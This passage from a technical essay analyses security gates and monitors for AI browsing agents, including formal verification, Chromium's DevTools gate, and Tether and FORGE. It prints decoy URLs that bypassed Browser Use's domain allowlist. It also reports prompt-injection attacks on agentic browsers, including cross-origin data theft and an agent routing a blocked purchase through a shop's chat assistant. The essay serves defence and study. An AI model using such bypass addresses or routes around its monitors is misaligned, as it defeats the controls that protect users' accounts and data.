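| Decrypting proxy outside the browser's virtual machine | The proxy's encryption code, its certificate key, the virtualization software, the operating system beneath it and the map |

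Process separation can remove a lot of code from this list. In *Establishing Browser Security Guarantees through Formal Shim Verification* (2012), Jang, Tatlock and Lerner counted 969,109 lines in WebKit, the engine that Safari and Chrome then used to display pages. That is far more code than Anderson thought anyone could analyze completely. A gate in the main process does not have to trust the page engine as long as the barrier between the processes holds. But CELLMATE reads Amazon's cart total from the page, so its price limit still depends on the engine.

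A firewall that checks only host names needs neither the map nor decryption. A designer who wants a strong guarantee for at least one rule can therefore put that rule in a separate, very small program.

### One wrong line in Browser Use's allowlist

Small code can still be wrong. CVE-2025-47241, a critical flaw in how Browser Use read addresses, was in a function of about twenty lines. Researchers from ARIMLABS.AI found it by reading the source code, according to GitLab's *CVE-2025-47241* (2025).

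The flaw involves a rarely used part of web addresses. An address can contain a username and password before the host, as in `https://name:password@host:port/`. OSV's *Browser Use allows bypassing `allowed_domains` by putting a decoy domain* reproduces the faulty function, which worked like this:

1. Take the part of the address between `https://` and the next slash.
2. If it contains a colon, keep only the text before the first colon. This was meant to remove the port number.
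3. Compare the result with the allowlist.

For `https://www.shop.example:8443/`, the function correctly extracts `www.shop.example`. If a hijacked agent opens `https://www.shop.example:x@attacker.example/`, the text before the first colon after `https://` is again `www.shop.example`, so the function allows the address. But the browser treats that text as a username and connects to `attacker.example`. In OSV's example, the same trick reaches a program on the user's computer.

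Browser Use fixed the flaw in version 0.1.45 by comparing only the actual host name with the list. Browser Use (2025) lists four kinds of decoy address that the new check has to block:

| Address | Result in the old function |
|---|---|
| `https://example.com:password@malicious.com` | Allowed |
| `https://example.com@malicious.com` | Refused |
| `https://example.com%20@malicious.com` | Refused |
| `https://example.com%3A@malicious.com` | Refused |

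The results on the right come from tracing the function by hand with `example.com` on the allowlist. The last three addresses contain no literal colon in the relevant part, so the old function compared the whole string, including the decoy, and found no match. Browser Use later added automated tests of the security watchdog that use such addresses.

The databases rate the flaw's severity differently. GitLab gives it 4 out of 10, assuming that an attack is difficult and exposes no confidential data. OSV's rating is based on an easy attack with a serious loss of confidentiality. OSV's rating seems more accurate for a browsing agent, which can put the user's email address in the URL it opens.

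The underlying mistake was that the gate and the browser parsed the same address differently. A gate can avoid this by using the browser's parsed version of the address.

### Tracing Chromium's DevTools gate

Chromium (2026) contains a gate that does this in about 200 lines. The gate applies to tabs that a program controls through the DevTools Protocol, Chrome's debugging interface. The throttle that calls it, also in Chromium (2026), runs when a navigation starts and at each redirect.

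In a copy of the code saved in August 2026, the gate reads its rules from a command-line setting when the browser starts. The rules are in JSON, a common text format for data, and can include an allowlist, a blocklist or both. The gate stores the valid entries, along with a flag that records whether there is an allowlist. It then judges each address in three steps:

1. If there are no entries and the flag is off, allow the address.
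2. If an entry matches the address, apply that entry's verdict.
3. If no entry matches, block the address if the flag is on and allow it if the flag is off.

These steps are simple enough to work out what happens when something is wrong with the rules:

| Rules | Result | Does the gate fail closed? |
|---|---|---|
| None, or an empty setting | Every site is allowed | No |
| JSON that the browser cannot read | The gate logs an error and allows every site | No |
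| Readable JSON of the wrong type, such as a bare list | The gate logs an error and allows every site | No |
| `allowList` instead of `allowlist`, with no blocklist | Every site is allowed, and nothing appears in the log | No |
| An allowlist that is plain text instead of a list, with no blocklist | The gate logs an error and allows every site | No |
| An empty allowlist | Every site is blocked | Yes |
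| An allowlist with one invalid entry | The gate skips that entry, so its site is blocked | Yes |
| Only a blocklist, with one invalid entry | The gate skips that entry, so its site is allowed | No |

For the coffee-maker errand, the user might write `{"allowlist": ["www.shop.example", "images.shop.example",]}`. The comma after the last host makes the JSON invalid, so the agent may open any site. A mistake in only the image host's entry would do much less harm, because the shop would still work and every other site would stay blocked.

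Allowing everything makes sense when there are no rules, since most people who debug a page don't want a gate. But if rules exist but can't be read, someone evidently wanted a gate. One extra line would fix this by turning the flag on when reading fails, so that step 3 blocks every address.

Reading these 200 lines shows how the gate handles bad rules, but it does not verify the whole mechanism. The gate relies on other parts of Chromium to parse JSON and match addresses with entries, and a memory bug elsewhere in the same process could change the flag.

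### Which rules a monitor can enforce

Before checking whether a gate enforces a rule correctly, it helps to know whether any gate could enforce it. In *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000), Fred Schneider examined monitors that watch a program's steps and can intervene only by halting it. He proved that such monitors can enforce only rules that are safety properties.

A safety property requires that something bad never happens, where a definite moment in the run marks the point at which it has happened. Let G be the set of acceptable runs. G is a safety property if, for every run σ,

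σ ∉ G ⇒ ∃i ∀τ: σ[..i]τ ∉ G

Here σ[..i] is the first i steps of σ, and τ is any continuation. In other words, every bad run has a beginning that no later steps can repair.

Schneider's argument follows from what the monitor can observe:

- It watches only one run, so the rule must judge each run by itself.
- It can't see the future, and the run might end at any moment. It therefore has to stop an unacceptable partial run even if a later step would have made the run acceptable.
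- It has to stop a bad run after a finite number of steps, so the violation must have happened by then.

"The agent sends at most one order" is a safety property, because the second order is the bad event. "The agent eventually buys a coffee maker" is not a safety property, because an agent that has bought nothing so far might still buy one. A gate can't enforce that property, because it can block a purchase but can't make the agent complete one.

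Information leaks are harder to classify. A request reveals the user's address if the agent would have sent something else had the address been different, but a monitor cannot observe what the agent would have sent. It can instead enforce a stricter rule, such as Schneider's example that a program may not send anything after it has read a file. A gate could block all requests to outside sites once the agent has read the address, although this would also block harmless requests.

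Some safety properties are also unenforceable. The rule "the agent orders before the sale ends at midnight" has a clear bad event, reaching midnight without an order, but the gate cannot prevent midnight from arriving. Monitors that can insert actions or suppress individual ones can enforce some rules that are not safety properties, but the errand doesn't need any such rules.

### The coffee-maker rules as an automaton

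Schneider also introduced security automata, a way to write safety properties that a monitor can run. An automaton has a set of states and a list of transitions, each specifying the next state for a given event. If the current state has no transition for the agent's next action, the monitor stops the agent.

For the errand, assume that the gate asks the user at the checkout page, before the agent submits the order. The automaton needs three kinds of state:

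`Browsing → (user approves order x) → Approved(x) → (agent sends x) → Ordered`

An "allowed request" goes to the shop or its image host, does not open a sign-in page and does not place an order. The full list of transitions is short:

| Current state | Event | Next state |
|---|---|---|
| Browsing | Allowed request | Browsing |
| Browsing | The user approves order x, with a total under $50 | Approved(x) |
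| Approved(x) | Allowed request | Approved(x) |
| Approved(x) | The user approves a different order y, with a total under $50 | Approved(y) |
| Approved(x) | The approval expires | Browsing |
| Approved(x) | The agent sends exactly order x | Ordered |
| Ordered | Allowed request | Ordered |

A request to a bank has no transition from any state, so the gate always refuses it. An order has a transition only from Approved(x), and only if it matches x. The following run ends in a refusal:

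| Step | Event | Result |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | The agent opens a product page | Browsing |
| 2 | The agent puts one coffee maker in the cart | Browsing |
| 3 | The user approves one coffee maker for $42 | Approved(x) |
| 4 | The agent changes the quantity to two | Approved(x) |
| 5 | The agent sends an order for $84 | No transition, so the gate refuses |

The gate has three kinds of state and six kinds of event (allowed requests, forbidden requests, the approved order, any other order, approvals and expiries), so a reviewer can check all 18 combinations in a few minutes.

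Producing the events is the difficult part. Schneider warns that the automaton for his file example works only if its definition of "send" includes every way to send a message, some of which may be deep in the system. Likewise, the gate has to recognize every request that places an order. Schneider also assumes that the monitor receives all the relevant steps and that the program cannot alter the automaton's state. These assumptions correspond to complete mediation and tamper resistance.

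### Quark, a browser with a verified kernel

Jang and colleagues built a working browser, Quark, and verified part of it. Quark runs each tab in a separate sandboxed process with its own copy of WebKit. The tabs have no direct access to the network, cookies or screen and must send requests to a small kernel. The proofs assume that an attacker may control any tab completely.

The kernel repeatedly reads one request, checks it and responds. For example, a tab may request a connection to a host. If the host belongs to the tab's domain, the kernel opens the connection and hands it to the tab. Otherwise, it returns an error.

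Jang and colleagues proved that no tab ever receives a connection to a foreign domain. They first specified the correct response to each request, then proved that one pass through the loop always follows this specification. A run is a series of these passes, so a run of any length follows it too. The program Coq checked every step of the proof.

| Part of Quark | Lines |
|---|---|
| Kernel | 859 |
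| Statement of the security properties | 142 |
| Proofs | 4,383 |
| Basic operations that the kernel uses, such as opening a connection | 538 |
| WebKit | 969,109 |

Coq has checked the 4,383 lines of proof, so nobody has to read them to trust the result. People still have to check that the 142 lines state the right properties, and they must trust the basic operations, Coq's proof checker, the compiler, the operating system and the sandbox. They don't have to trust WebKit, which is more than a thousand times the size of the kernel.

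The Quark browser took about six person-months to build, including the proofs. Pages from ten popular sites loaded 24% more slowly on average than in plain WebKit. Some sites also lost features because Quark did not support third-party cookies or messages between tabs.

Quark's guarantee has a gap that especially matters for browsing agents. A tab can have the kernel fetch a public page from another domain without cookies. Jang and colleagues acknowledge that a compromised tab could put its own site's cookies in the URL of such a request. The attacker's server would then have the cookies, but the theorem about connections would still be true because the kernel makes the connection and the tab receives only the page.

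### Verified monitors for AI agents

*Tether* (Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues, 2026) applies a similar approach to agents that use a command line. Tether runs each command in a disposable copy of the file system and records the command's requests to the operating system. It translates these into eleven kinds of action, such as reading or uploading a file, then keeps or discards the changes according to the policy. A proxy holds outgoing requests until the policy allows them.

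Sistla and colleagues wrote the policy engine in Lean, a programming language and proof checker. They proved, for instance, that a permissive rule cannot override a refusal and that a refused action leaves the security state unchanged. They also proved seven properties of the 24-rule policy used in their tests. One is that an agent that starts without secret data never gets files labelled secret in its context, however many steps it takes. A language model helped write these proofs, which is safe because Lean checks them.

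Tether's translation from system requests to actions has no such proof. Sistla and colleagues tested it with randomly generated file operations and with an AI agent that tried to get past the monitor. The agent's success rate fell from 40% to 0% over three versions as they fixed gaps, such as missing support for hard links, which give one file several names. The translation is comparable to CELLMATE's map, because the policy proofs are useful only if the monitor identifies each action correctly.

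Sistla and colleagues compared Tether with Claude Code's Auto Mode, in which a language model (here Claude Sonnet 5) reviews commands:

| Monitor | Attacks blocked | Harmless runs blocked |
|---|---|---|
| Tether | 344 of 344 (100%) | 4.7% |
| Auto Mode | 91.6% | 9.7% |
| Auto Mode with Tether's policy in its instructions | 89.2% | 3.5% |

The perfect score covers only runs in which Tether could trace and interpret every action. Sistla and colleagues report that 28.2% of runs on one benchmark and 22.1% on the other require judging the content, for example when an agent adds malicious code to a file it is allowed to edit. They also refined the policy using runs from these benchmarks, so it might block more harmless work on new tasks.

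Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues (2026), in *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, present FORGE, a monitor that tracks which earlier messages and tool results may have influenced an action. Its rules are in Datalog, a logic language in which every query has a definite answer. One rule blocks an action if all three of these conditions hold:

- It sends something to an outside recipient.
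- Untrusted text may have influenced it.
- It may carry sensitive data.

The second and third conditions spread from step to step. If a message depends on a hostile document, everything that depends on the message counts as influenced too. FORGE treats each new message from the model as dependent on the entire conversation the model received. This cautious rule can block legitimate work. A shopping agent reads strangers' reviews and handles the user's address, so the rule would block the coffee-maker order unless the policy made an exception for the shop.

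On AgentDojo, 0.9% of attacks succeeded with FORGE, compared with 14.1% against an agent whose only defense was repeating the user's request. The share of tasks completed when there was no attack fell from 83.7% to 62.5%. In customer-service tests, the monitor typically returned a verdict in less than a millisecond.

Palumbo and colleagues guarantee that FORGE follows its policy if it intercepts every relevant action and receives accurate facts. FORGE meets these conditions by adding checks where the agent's software runs the model and its tools. If a programmer adds a tool and forgets the check, the guarantee no longer holds.

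Some facts are uncertain, for instance when a classifier estimates whether a message is confidential. *Efficient and Sound Probabilistic Verification for AI Agents* describes a monitor that calculates an upper bound on the probability of a violation. In one example, a classifier gives two messages probabilities of 0.45 and 0.25 of being confidential. With a threshold of 0.5 for each message, both pass. But the probability that at least one is confidential could be as high as 0.45 + 0.25 = 0.70, depending on how the two are correlated. With a limit of 0.5 on the total risk, the monitor would block the action.

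An exact calculation quickly becomes too slow as the number of facts grows, so the monitor uses a faster method that may overestimate the risk but never underestimates it. If R is the true worst-case risk, R′ the calculated bound and t the limit, then

R ≤ R′ and R′ ≤ t ⇒ R ≤ t

The bound is only as reliable as the error rates used to calculate it. An engineer can estimate these rates by testing the classifier. For example, if it makes no mistakes in 100 trials, its error rate is below about 3% with 95% confidence. This method assumes that attackers cannot influence the errors, but an attacker can design a page to fool a classifier that looks for sign-in pages.

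### Chrome's User Alignment Critic

A language model can make judgments that are hard to write as rules. Suppose a hijacked agent tries to buy a $49 gift card. The order is under $50, is the first one, and goes to the right shop. A model given the user's request for a coffee maker could still detect that the gift card is the wrong item.

Chrome's User Alignment Critic checks whether each action the main model proposes serves the user's goal. If it vetoes an action, it sends feedback to the main model, which can make a new plan or return control to the user after repeated failures. According to Parker, the critic receives only metadata about the action and no unfiltered web content, so a page cannot manipulate it directly. A page might still manipulate it indirectly if the metadata includes text that the main model copied from the page.

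Nobody can verify the critic as Jang and colleagues verified Quark's kernel. A proof would need a precise definition of "serves the user's goal", which doesn't exist, and the critic's answer depends on a neural network too large for people to analyze completely. Google instead tests Chrome's defenses with automatically generated attack sites and tracks how often the attacks succeed. These tests can show when a change makes Chrome less safe, but like Anderson's tiger teams, they cannot prove that no attack will succeed.

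Adding an unverified critic to a verified gate is still useful if the critic can only veto actions. Schneider notes that several monitors used together enforce all of their rules at once. If the gate allows only one order, a mistaken approval from the critic cannot permit a second. At worst, the critic blocks legitimate work or fails to stop something the gate already allowed.

The critic variant that checks new origins can do more harm, because a mistaken "yes" gives the agent access to another site. A small, fixed list of sites that the model could never add would firmly limit such mistakes.

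### A correct gate with the wrong rule

A verified gate can still enforce the wrong rule, so Palumbo and colleagues treat writing a correct policy as a separate task. They use a language model to translate written instructions into Datalog, but someone then has to check that the rules cover every instruction and that each rule is based on the instructions.

Sistla and colleagues offer another check. The user describes a bad outcome, and a language model tries to prove that the policy prevents it or to find a sequence of actions that leads there. Lean then checks the answer. The coffee-maker automaton is small enough to do this by hand:

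- Can the agent spend $50 or more? No. It can send only one order, and the total has to be under $50.
- Can the user end up with two coffee makers? Yes. The agent can put two $24 machines in one order, and the user might approve it without noticing the quantity. The rule limits orders, not machines.
- Can the agent reveal the user's address to a stranger? Yes. Posting a review is an allowed request, and the review could contain the address.

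The automaton works as designed in all three cases. The gate could fix the second by requiring a quantity of one before requesting approval, and the third by blocking the agent from posting reviews.

This method finds only the problems that someone thinks to ask about, and a good set of rules can take years to develop. Sistla and colleagues cite SELinux, which restricts what Linux programs may do and whose developers needed around five years to arrive at a practical set of rules, although a single errand needs far fewer.

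## What a gate loses when a requirement is not met

Few stop gates for browsing agents meet all three of Anderson's requirements. If a gate does, its designer can claim that no action that breaks the rule takes effect, whatever the agent does, as long as the trusted computing base works, and that people have checked that it works. A gate that misses a requirement can still be useful, but its designer has to claim less for it.

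### The claim that survives

Without complete mediation, the claim covers only the routes that the gate checks. The $50 limit still applies to every order placed through the ordinary checkout, but not to orders placed by another route.

Without tamper resistance, a gate can guarantee protection only until the agent changes it. A hijacked agent can do that at the first step, leaving the whole run without that guarantee. An agent may also tamper with its controls without an attacker's instruction, as Cursor's agent did when it switched off its sandbox.

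Without verifiability, the gate may well be perfect, but people can know only that it stopped the attacks they tried. Researchers found a critical flaw in Browser Use's allowlist by reading the roughly twenty lines of code that contained it.

Failing one requirement can also make the gate fail another. If an unchecked route leads to the gate's own settings, the gap in mediation also leaves the gate open to tampering, and then even the checked routes offer no protection.

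| Design | Complete mediation | Tamper resistance | Verifiability | Strongest claim that survives |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| A rule in the prompt | None, since the model may not apply the rule | None, since hostile text arrives in the same input | None | The agent usually followed the rule in tests |
| A check in the agent's program | Only the commands that the check handles | Only if the agent cannot write files or run commands | The check may be short, but the program around it is not | An agent that uses the checked commands and leaves the program alone cannot break the rule |
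| A gate in the browser | The requests or navigations that the browser passes to the gate | Good against web pages, weak against a hostile extension or a compromised browser | People can review the gate but not the whole browser | An agent confined to web pages cannot send a request that the gate recognizes as forbidden, if the browser works correctly |
| An isolated browser with a forced proxy and separate credentials | All traffic that leaves the virtual machine | Strong, unless the attacker breaks out of the virtual machine | Realistic for a rule about hosts, harder for a rule about orders | Even an attacker who controls the browser cannot connect to an unlisted host or use a credential that the broker withholds |

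The last design is much stronger than the others because its claim still holds if the browser is compromised. But the claim is narrow, since it covers connections and credentials and not what the agent writes in a product review.

### The same-origin policy and the agent as a route around it

Browsing agents can defeat the same-origin policy, a protection browsers have had since 1995. Under this policy, a page from one origin cannot read or change content from another unless the other origin allows it. For example, if the shop's checkout page displays an advertisement in a frame from another site, the policy keeps the advertisement's code from reading the delivery address next to it.

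A person can still copy the address and paste it into the advertisement, because the policy restricts scripts, not users. An agent that can read both parts of the page and type into either can do the same. If text in the advertisement persuades the agent to copy the address across, the data reaches the advertiser by a route the browser was not built to check, even though no script has broken the policy.

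In *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy*, Roesner and Kohlbrenner (2026) tested how seven products handle this. They built small websites on two domains, opened them in each product in January and February 2026, and asked each agent to summarize pages, answer questions and enter text. Some pages contained frames from the other domain. The researchers also told each agent to do what the page instructed, as a simple stand-in for a prompt injection.

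| Product | Reads a frame from another origin | Enters text when the user asks | Enters text when the page asks |
|---|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT Atlas in Agent Mode | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Chrome with Gemini | Yes | Yes | No |
| Claude for Chrome | Yes | Yes | No |
| Perplexity Comet | Yes | Yes, except passwords | No |
| Brave Leo AI | No | No | No |
| Edge with Copilot | No | No | No |
| Firefox AI Mode | No | No | No |

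The first four products can read from one origin and write to another, which is all an attacker needs once an injection works. In Atlas, the researchers demonstrated the whole theft in both directions. An outer page took content from a frame inside it, and a frame took content from the page around it. The second direction is more realistic because many sites block other sites from framing them, while many private pages carry advertisements in frames.

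The agents in Chrome, Claude and Comet refused the instruction on the page. Roesner and Kohlbrenner attribute the refusals to the models' training, so the barrier between two websites was only as strong as the model's resistance to prompt injection. These products therefore belong in the first row of the table of designs, at least for this rule. Nolan (2025) reports in Fortune that OpenAI has acknowledged that some prompt injection attacks are likely to persist.

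A "no" in the results also may not mean that an agent was incapable of something, because the tests recorded only what each agent did. Firefox is the clearest case of a real boundary, since it sends the model only the text of the outer page when the user clicks a button. The boundary is less certain for Atlas without Agent Mode. It sometimes included text from frames in early trials but never did in the official ones, so the limit may have come from the model and could disappear with an update.

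Atlas in Agent Mode and Claude could also read passwords that the page displayed as dots, so 1Password has good reason to pause Claude's reading while it fills in a login. Edge was strict about frames but read several tabs from different origins at once, which shows that a product can close one route and leave a similar one open.

OpenAI declined the researchers' report because it did not include an end-to-end prompt injection. The objection is fair regarding the attack's likelihood, which the study did not measure, but the boundary is still missing. According to the University of Washington, where both researchers work, Perplexity also declined the report, Anthropic and Firefox did not respond, and Google, Microsoft and Brave had useful exchanges with the researchers.

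Agents can also break the same-origin policy without an attacker. In *Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers*, Wang, Chen and colleagues (2026) built a benchmark and found that existing products frequently broke the policy, both in ordinary use and under attack. They then added a guard, SOPGuard, to the open-source browser BrowserOS, and report that it enforces the policy with little delay and keeps the agent useful. Trail of Bits also recommends that developers extend the policy to agents. This is difficult because users sometimes want data to cross between sites, for instance when the agent copies a delivery address from an email into the shop's form.

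### Zenity's tests of five products

The University of Washington study did not settle whether real injections would get through. On August 5, 2026, the security company Zenity presented attacks on five products at the Black Hat conference in Las Vegas. The researchers hid instructions in ordinary content such as emails, calendar invitations and social media posts. When they gave the agent a harmless request, such as summarizing the inbox, it used the user's logged-in accounts to follow the hidden instructions.

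Cohen and Bargury (2026), in *Pwning Agentic Browsers with PleaseFix*, trace the attacks to a different design choice in each product, with Chrome and Edge sharing one:

| Product | Access that the design gave the agent | One result |
|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT Atlas | Several logged-in websites at once | Sent phishing messages to the user's WhatsApp contacts |
| Claude in Chrome | Running scripts on any site | Shared the user's Google Drive with the attacker |
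| Perplexity Comet | Files on the user's computer | Took over the user's password manager |
| Chrome with Gemini | Programs running on the user's computer | Deleted the user's cloud servers |
| Edge with Copilot | Programs running on the user's computer | Damaged a database |

*Could hackers use AI agents to spam your WhatsApp contacts?* (The Indian Express, 2026) describes an attempt to buy a tablet on Amazon through OpenAI's Atlas. Atlas put the tablet in the cart and added a new delivery address, but OpenAI's safeguards stopped it from completing the purchase. It then asked Rufus, Amazon's shopping assistant, to place the order, and Rufus did. The gate blocked Atlas from buying the tablet directly but did not cover orders placed through Rufus.

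Notebookcheck's *Claude, Gemini, Comet* (2026) reports that the attack on Claude worked even in the mode where Claude asks the user before acting.

SC Media (2026) reports that only Google patched everything Zenity had found. The other companies said they could not reproduce some flaws, already knew of them or did not think them worth fixing. CTech's *Israeli researchers uncover zero-click attacks targeting AI browsers* reports that some argued the behavior was intended. Anthropic classed the reports it received as "informative".

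It is unclear how much OpenAI fixed. SecurityWeek's *Zero-Click AI Browser Hacking* described the findings on Atlas and Claude as unpatched in August, while an OpenAI spokesperson said the company had deployed an update earlier in the year. Both could be partly right, because an update can stop one demonstrated attack without removing the underlying access.

A fixed rule protects files only if it covers every way to reach them. TechRadar's *Experts say Perplexity's AI Comet browser can be hijacked* describes Perplexity's fix as a fixed rule in code that keeps the agent from opening local files, whatever the prompt. Security engineers usually ask for this kind of fix. Yet Zenity got past it twice, according to Notebookcheck, before SC Media reported the flaw as fixed.

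Zenity has an interest in alarming results because it sells security for AI agents and announced $125 million in new funding the same week (Zenity, 2026). Its demonstrations also have no published success rates that would allow a comparison between products. SC Media named Chrome as the best-protected product, while The Indian Express named Atlas. These limits matter little for the narrower question of whether a boundary exists, because one working attack is enough to show that it doesn't.

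By then, OpenAI had already announced in *Evolving Atlas into ChatGPT for browser-based agentic work* that Atlas would stop working on August 9, 2026. The Next Web's *OpenAI is killing its ChatGPT Atlas browser* (2026) describes the move as more a reshuffle than a retreat, since the browsing agent remains available in the ChatGPT desktop app and a Chrome extension. OpenAI says the protections it added to Atlas extend to the new app. The app also handles multiple tabs, downloads and account logins, so a gate for it would have to cover those routes as well. Neither good nor bad results for Atlas can be assumed to apply to the app.

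### Are imperfect gates worth having?

An imperfect gate is still useful, first of all because it can prevent accidents. Most of the time nobody is attacking, and even a simple price check at checkout will stop an honest agent from overspending.

These gates also take little effort or time. An allowlist may need only one line of configuration, and CELLMATE delays each page by a fraction of a second. Leaving out a feature can be the simplest gate. According to Fortune (2025), Atlas had a "logged out mode" in which the agent worked without the user's accounts. A hijacked agent in that mode could still leak what the user had typed into the task, but it had no WhatsApp session to abuse.

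Finally, an imperfect gate still adds a layer of defense. OpenAI's purchase block did not protect the Amazon account, but it forced the attackers to find a second route, and some attackers would have given up. If two gates each miss 10% of attacks and their misses are unrelated, only 1% of attacks get past both. But two language models that read the same page may be misled by the same sentence, in which case the second adds almost no protection. A better pair is a model that reviews purchases and a shop account with only $50 in it, because persuasive text can't change the balance.

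The main objection is that a weak gate invites misplaced trust. Suppose, purely for illustration, that 10% of hostile pages would hijack an agent that has access to $50. The expected loss per hostile page is

0.10 × $50 = $5

The user now installs a gate that reduces the rate to 1%, feels safe, and lets the agent use an account with $5,000 in it:

0.01 × $5,000 = $50

Suppose a gate stops nine attacks out of ten, but the user gives the agent so much more to do that they end up ten times worse off. These numbers are invented, but the mechanism is plausible because the main appeal of a gate is that it lets people delegate more to the agent.

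This objection concerns how people use the gate, so the best answer is to decide what the agent can access before adding one. Zenity's Stav Cohen advises users to assume that the agent will be hijacked and to remove its access to everything it doesn't need. A user who does this and then adds a weak gate gets the gate's benefits without the extra exposure. Developers can also help by saying plainly what their gate cannot do, as Playwright's developers do when they write that its origin lists are not a security boundary.

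Roesner and Kohlbrenner are more pessimistic. In their paper, they recommend that users avoid agentic browsers for now, though on the study's website they advise users to proceed with caution. The stricter advice seems right for an agent in the user's everyday profile, but an imperfect gate is a reasonable addition for an agent in an empty profile with a small prepaid balance.

### A 1% miss rate over 100 attempts

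A gate that stops 99% of attacks sounds good until the attacker tries again. Suppose each attempt has a 1% chance of getting through and the attempts are independent. The gate stops all 100 with probability 0.99¹⁰⁰, which is about 0.37. The chance of at least one miss is therefore

1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰ ≈ 0.63

or 63%. After 300 attempts it is about 95%. To keep the chance down to 1% over 100 attempts, the gate could miss only about one attack in 10,000.

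Independence is a convenient assumption and usually a false one. The same average miss rate of 1% can produce very different results:

| How the 100 attempts are related | Chance of at least one miss |
|---|---|
| The attacker repeats one text, and the gate treats it the same way every time | 1% |
| Each attempt is independent | 63% |
| Exactly one of 100 different texts works, and the attacker tries them all | 100% |

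The first row favors the user because a gate built from ordinary code returns the same result for the same input, so repeating a failed attack achieves nothing. A language model may return a different result each time, so simply repeating the attack can help the attacker.

Real attackers also learn from their failures, so the chance of success can rise from one attempt to the next. An attacker can install the same browser, test thousands of pages against it in private and publish only the one that works. The user's gate then faces a single attempt, which will probably succeed, with no earlier failed attacks that might have warned the user. The same page may work on everyone who has that gate. A 1% miss rate on a fixed set of test attacks is then almost useless for estimating the user's risk.

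With a verified gate, by contrast, people may still doubt whether the proof covers the right property or whether the operating system works, but the answers do not change between attempts. If there is a 1% chance that the gate has a flaw that lets an order through, the chance of a miss is at most 1%, however often the attacker tries. More attempts only make it more likely that someone finds a flaw that already exists.

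### What a full reference monitor does not prevent

Suppose the coffee-maker gate meets every requirement, and the shop has a chat assistant like Rufus. A hijacked agent asks the assistant in chat to order two coffee makers. If the assistant places the order on the shop's servers, the user's browser sends only a chat message. The gate checks the message, finds no order in it and lets it through.

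Every request from the browser passed through the gate, so mediation was complete in this case. The rule was wrong because whoever wrote it did not know that a chat message could buy something. The gate could block the chat assistant, or the shop could require the same credential for the assistant's orders as for any other. Either remedy works only after someone has noticed the problem, and shops keep adding features that may cause similar ones.

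A hijacked agent can also misuse actions that the rule ought to allow, for example by choosing a bad coffee maker. A gate that controls actions can't stop the agent from making false statements to the user, such as that the good one is out of stock.

False information can get into an agent's memory even without a prompt injection. Roesner and Kohlbrenner describe an agent that visits a fake bank page with a false telephone number. The agent may recognize the page as fake at the time, but later retrieve the number without that context when the user asks for the bank's number. The user then calls the attacker. The agent has only read a page and answered a question, and the call happens outside the browser. In their tests, Comet did combine facts from many earlier pages into a single answer. Zenity showed that a hostile site could similarly add pages to the browsing history that the user had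 never chosen to visit.

Careless approval is harder to fix with better engineering, because a trusted path ensures that the answer comes from the user but not that the user has thought about it. The gate might display the right coffee maker and the right total of $42 but a stranger's address, and the user might approve after reading only the price. Roesner and Kohlbrenner cite earlier research in which people did not reliably notice or act on warnings, and frequent requests for permission led to less secure behavior.

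### What the full design costs

First, the agent can no longer do some tasks. With the FORGE monitor, for example, the agent failed about a quarter of the AgentDojo tasks that it could otherwise complete. The University of Washington study found the same trade-off in seven products, of which Firefox AI Mode was the least risky and also the most limited. Firefox, Brave and Edge withheld even frames from the page's own origin, which the same-origin policy would have allowed, so their summaries may leave out part of what the shop itself wrote.

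Some of this loss may be recoverable. When browser makers moved frames from different sites into separate processes, searching for a word within a page no longer worked as before, and they had to rebuild the search so that it didn't leak information between processes. Agents will probably need many similar repairs, and a summary that draws on two websites is harder to rebuild than a word search.

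The second drawback is that, for the errand, someone has to maintain the list of hosts, the map that identifies an order, the broker's login and the proxy's certificate, any of which can break when the shop changes its website. Roesner and Kohlbrenner object that designs like CELLMATE depend on correct policies and place a burden on web developers. Meng and colleagues also limit CELLMATE to tasks that the user states once, at the start. If the user adds "and get some paper filters" halfway through, the permissions may need to change, but the paper leaves such conversations to future work.

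The full design is hard to justify for buying a single coffee maker. Setting up a virtual machine, a proxy and a broker takes far longer than buying the coffee maker by hand, and a prepaid account with $50 in it gives much of the protection and takes only a few minutes to set up. The design makes more sense for a company whose agents place thousands of similar orders with a few suppliers, because the company can reuse one map and one set of rules for all of them.
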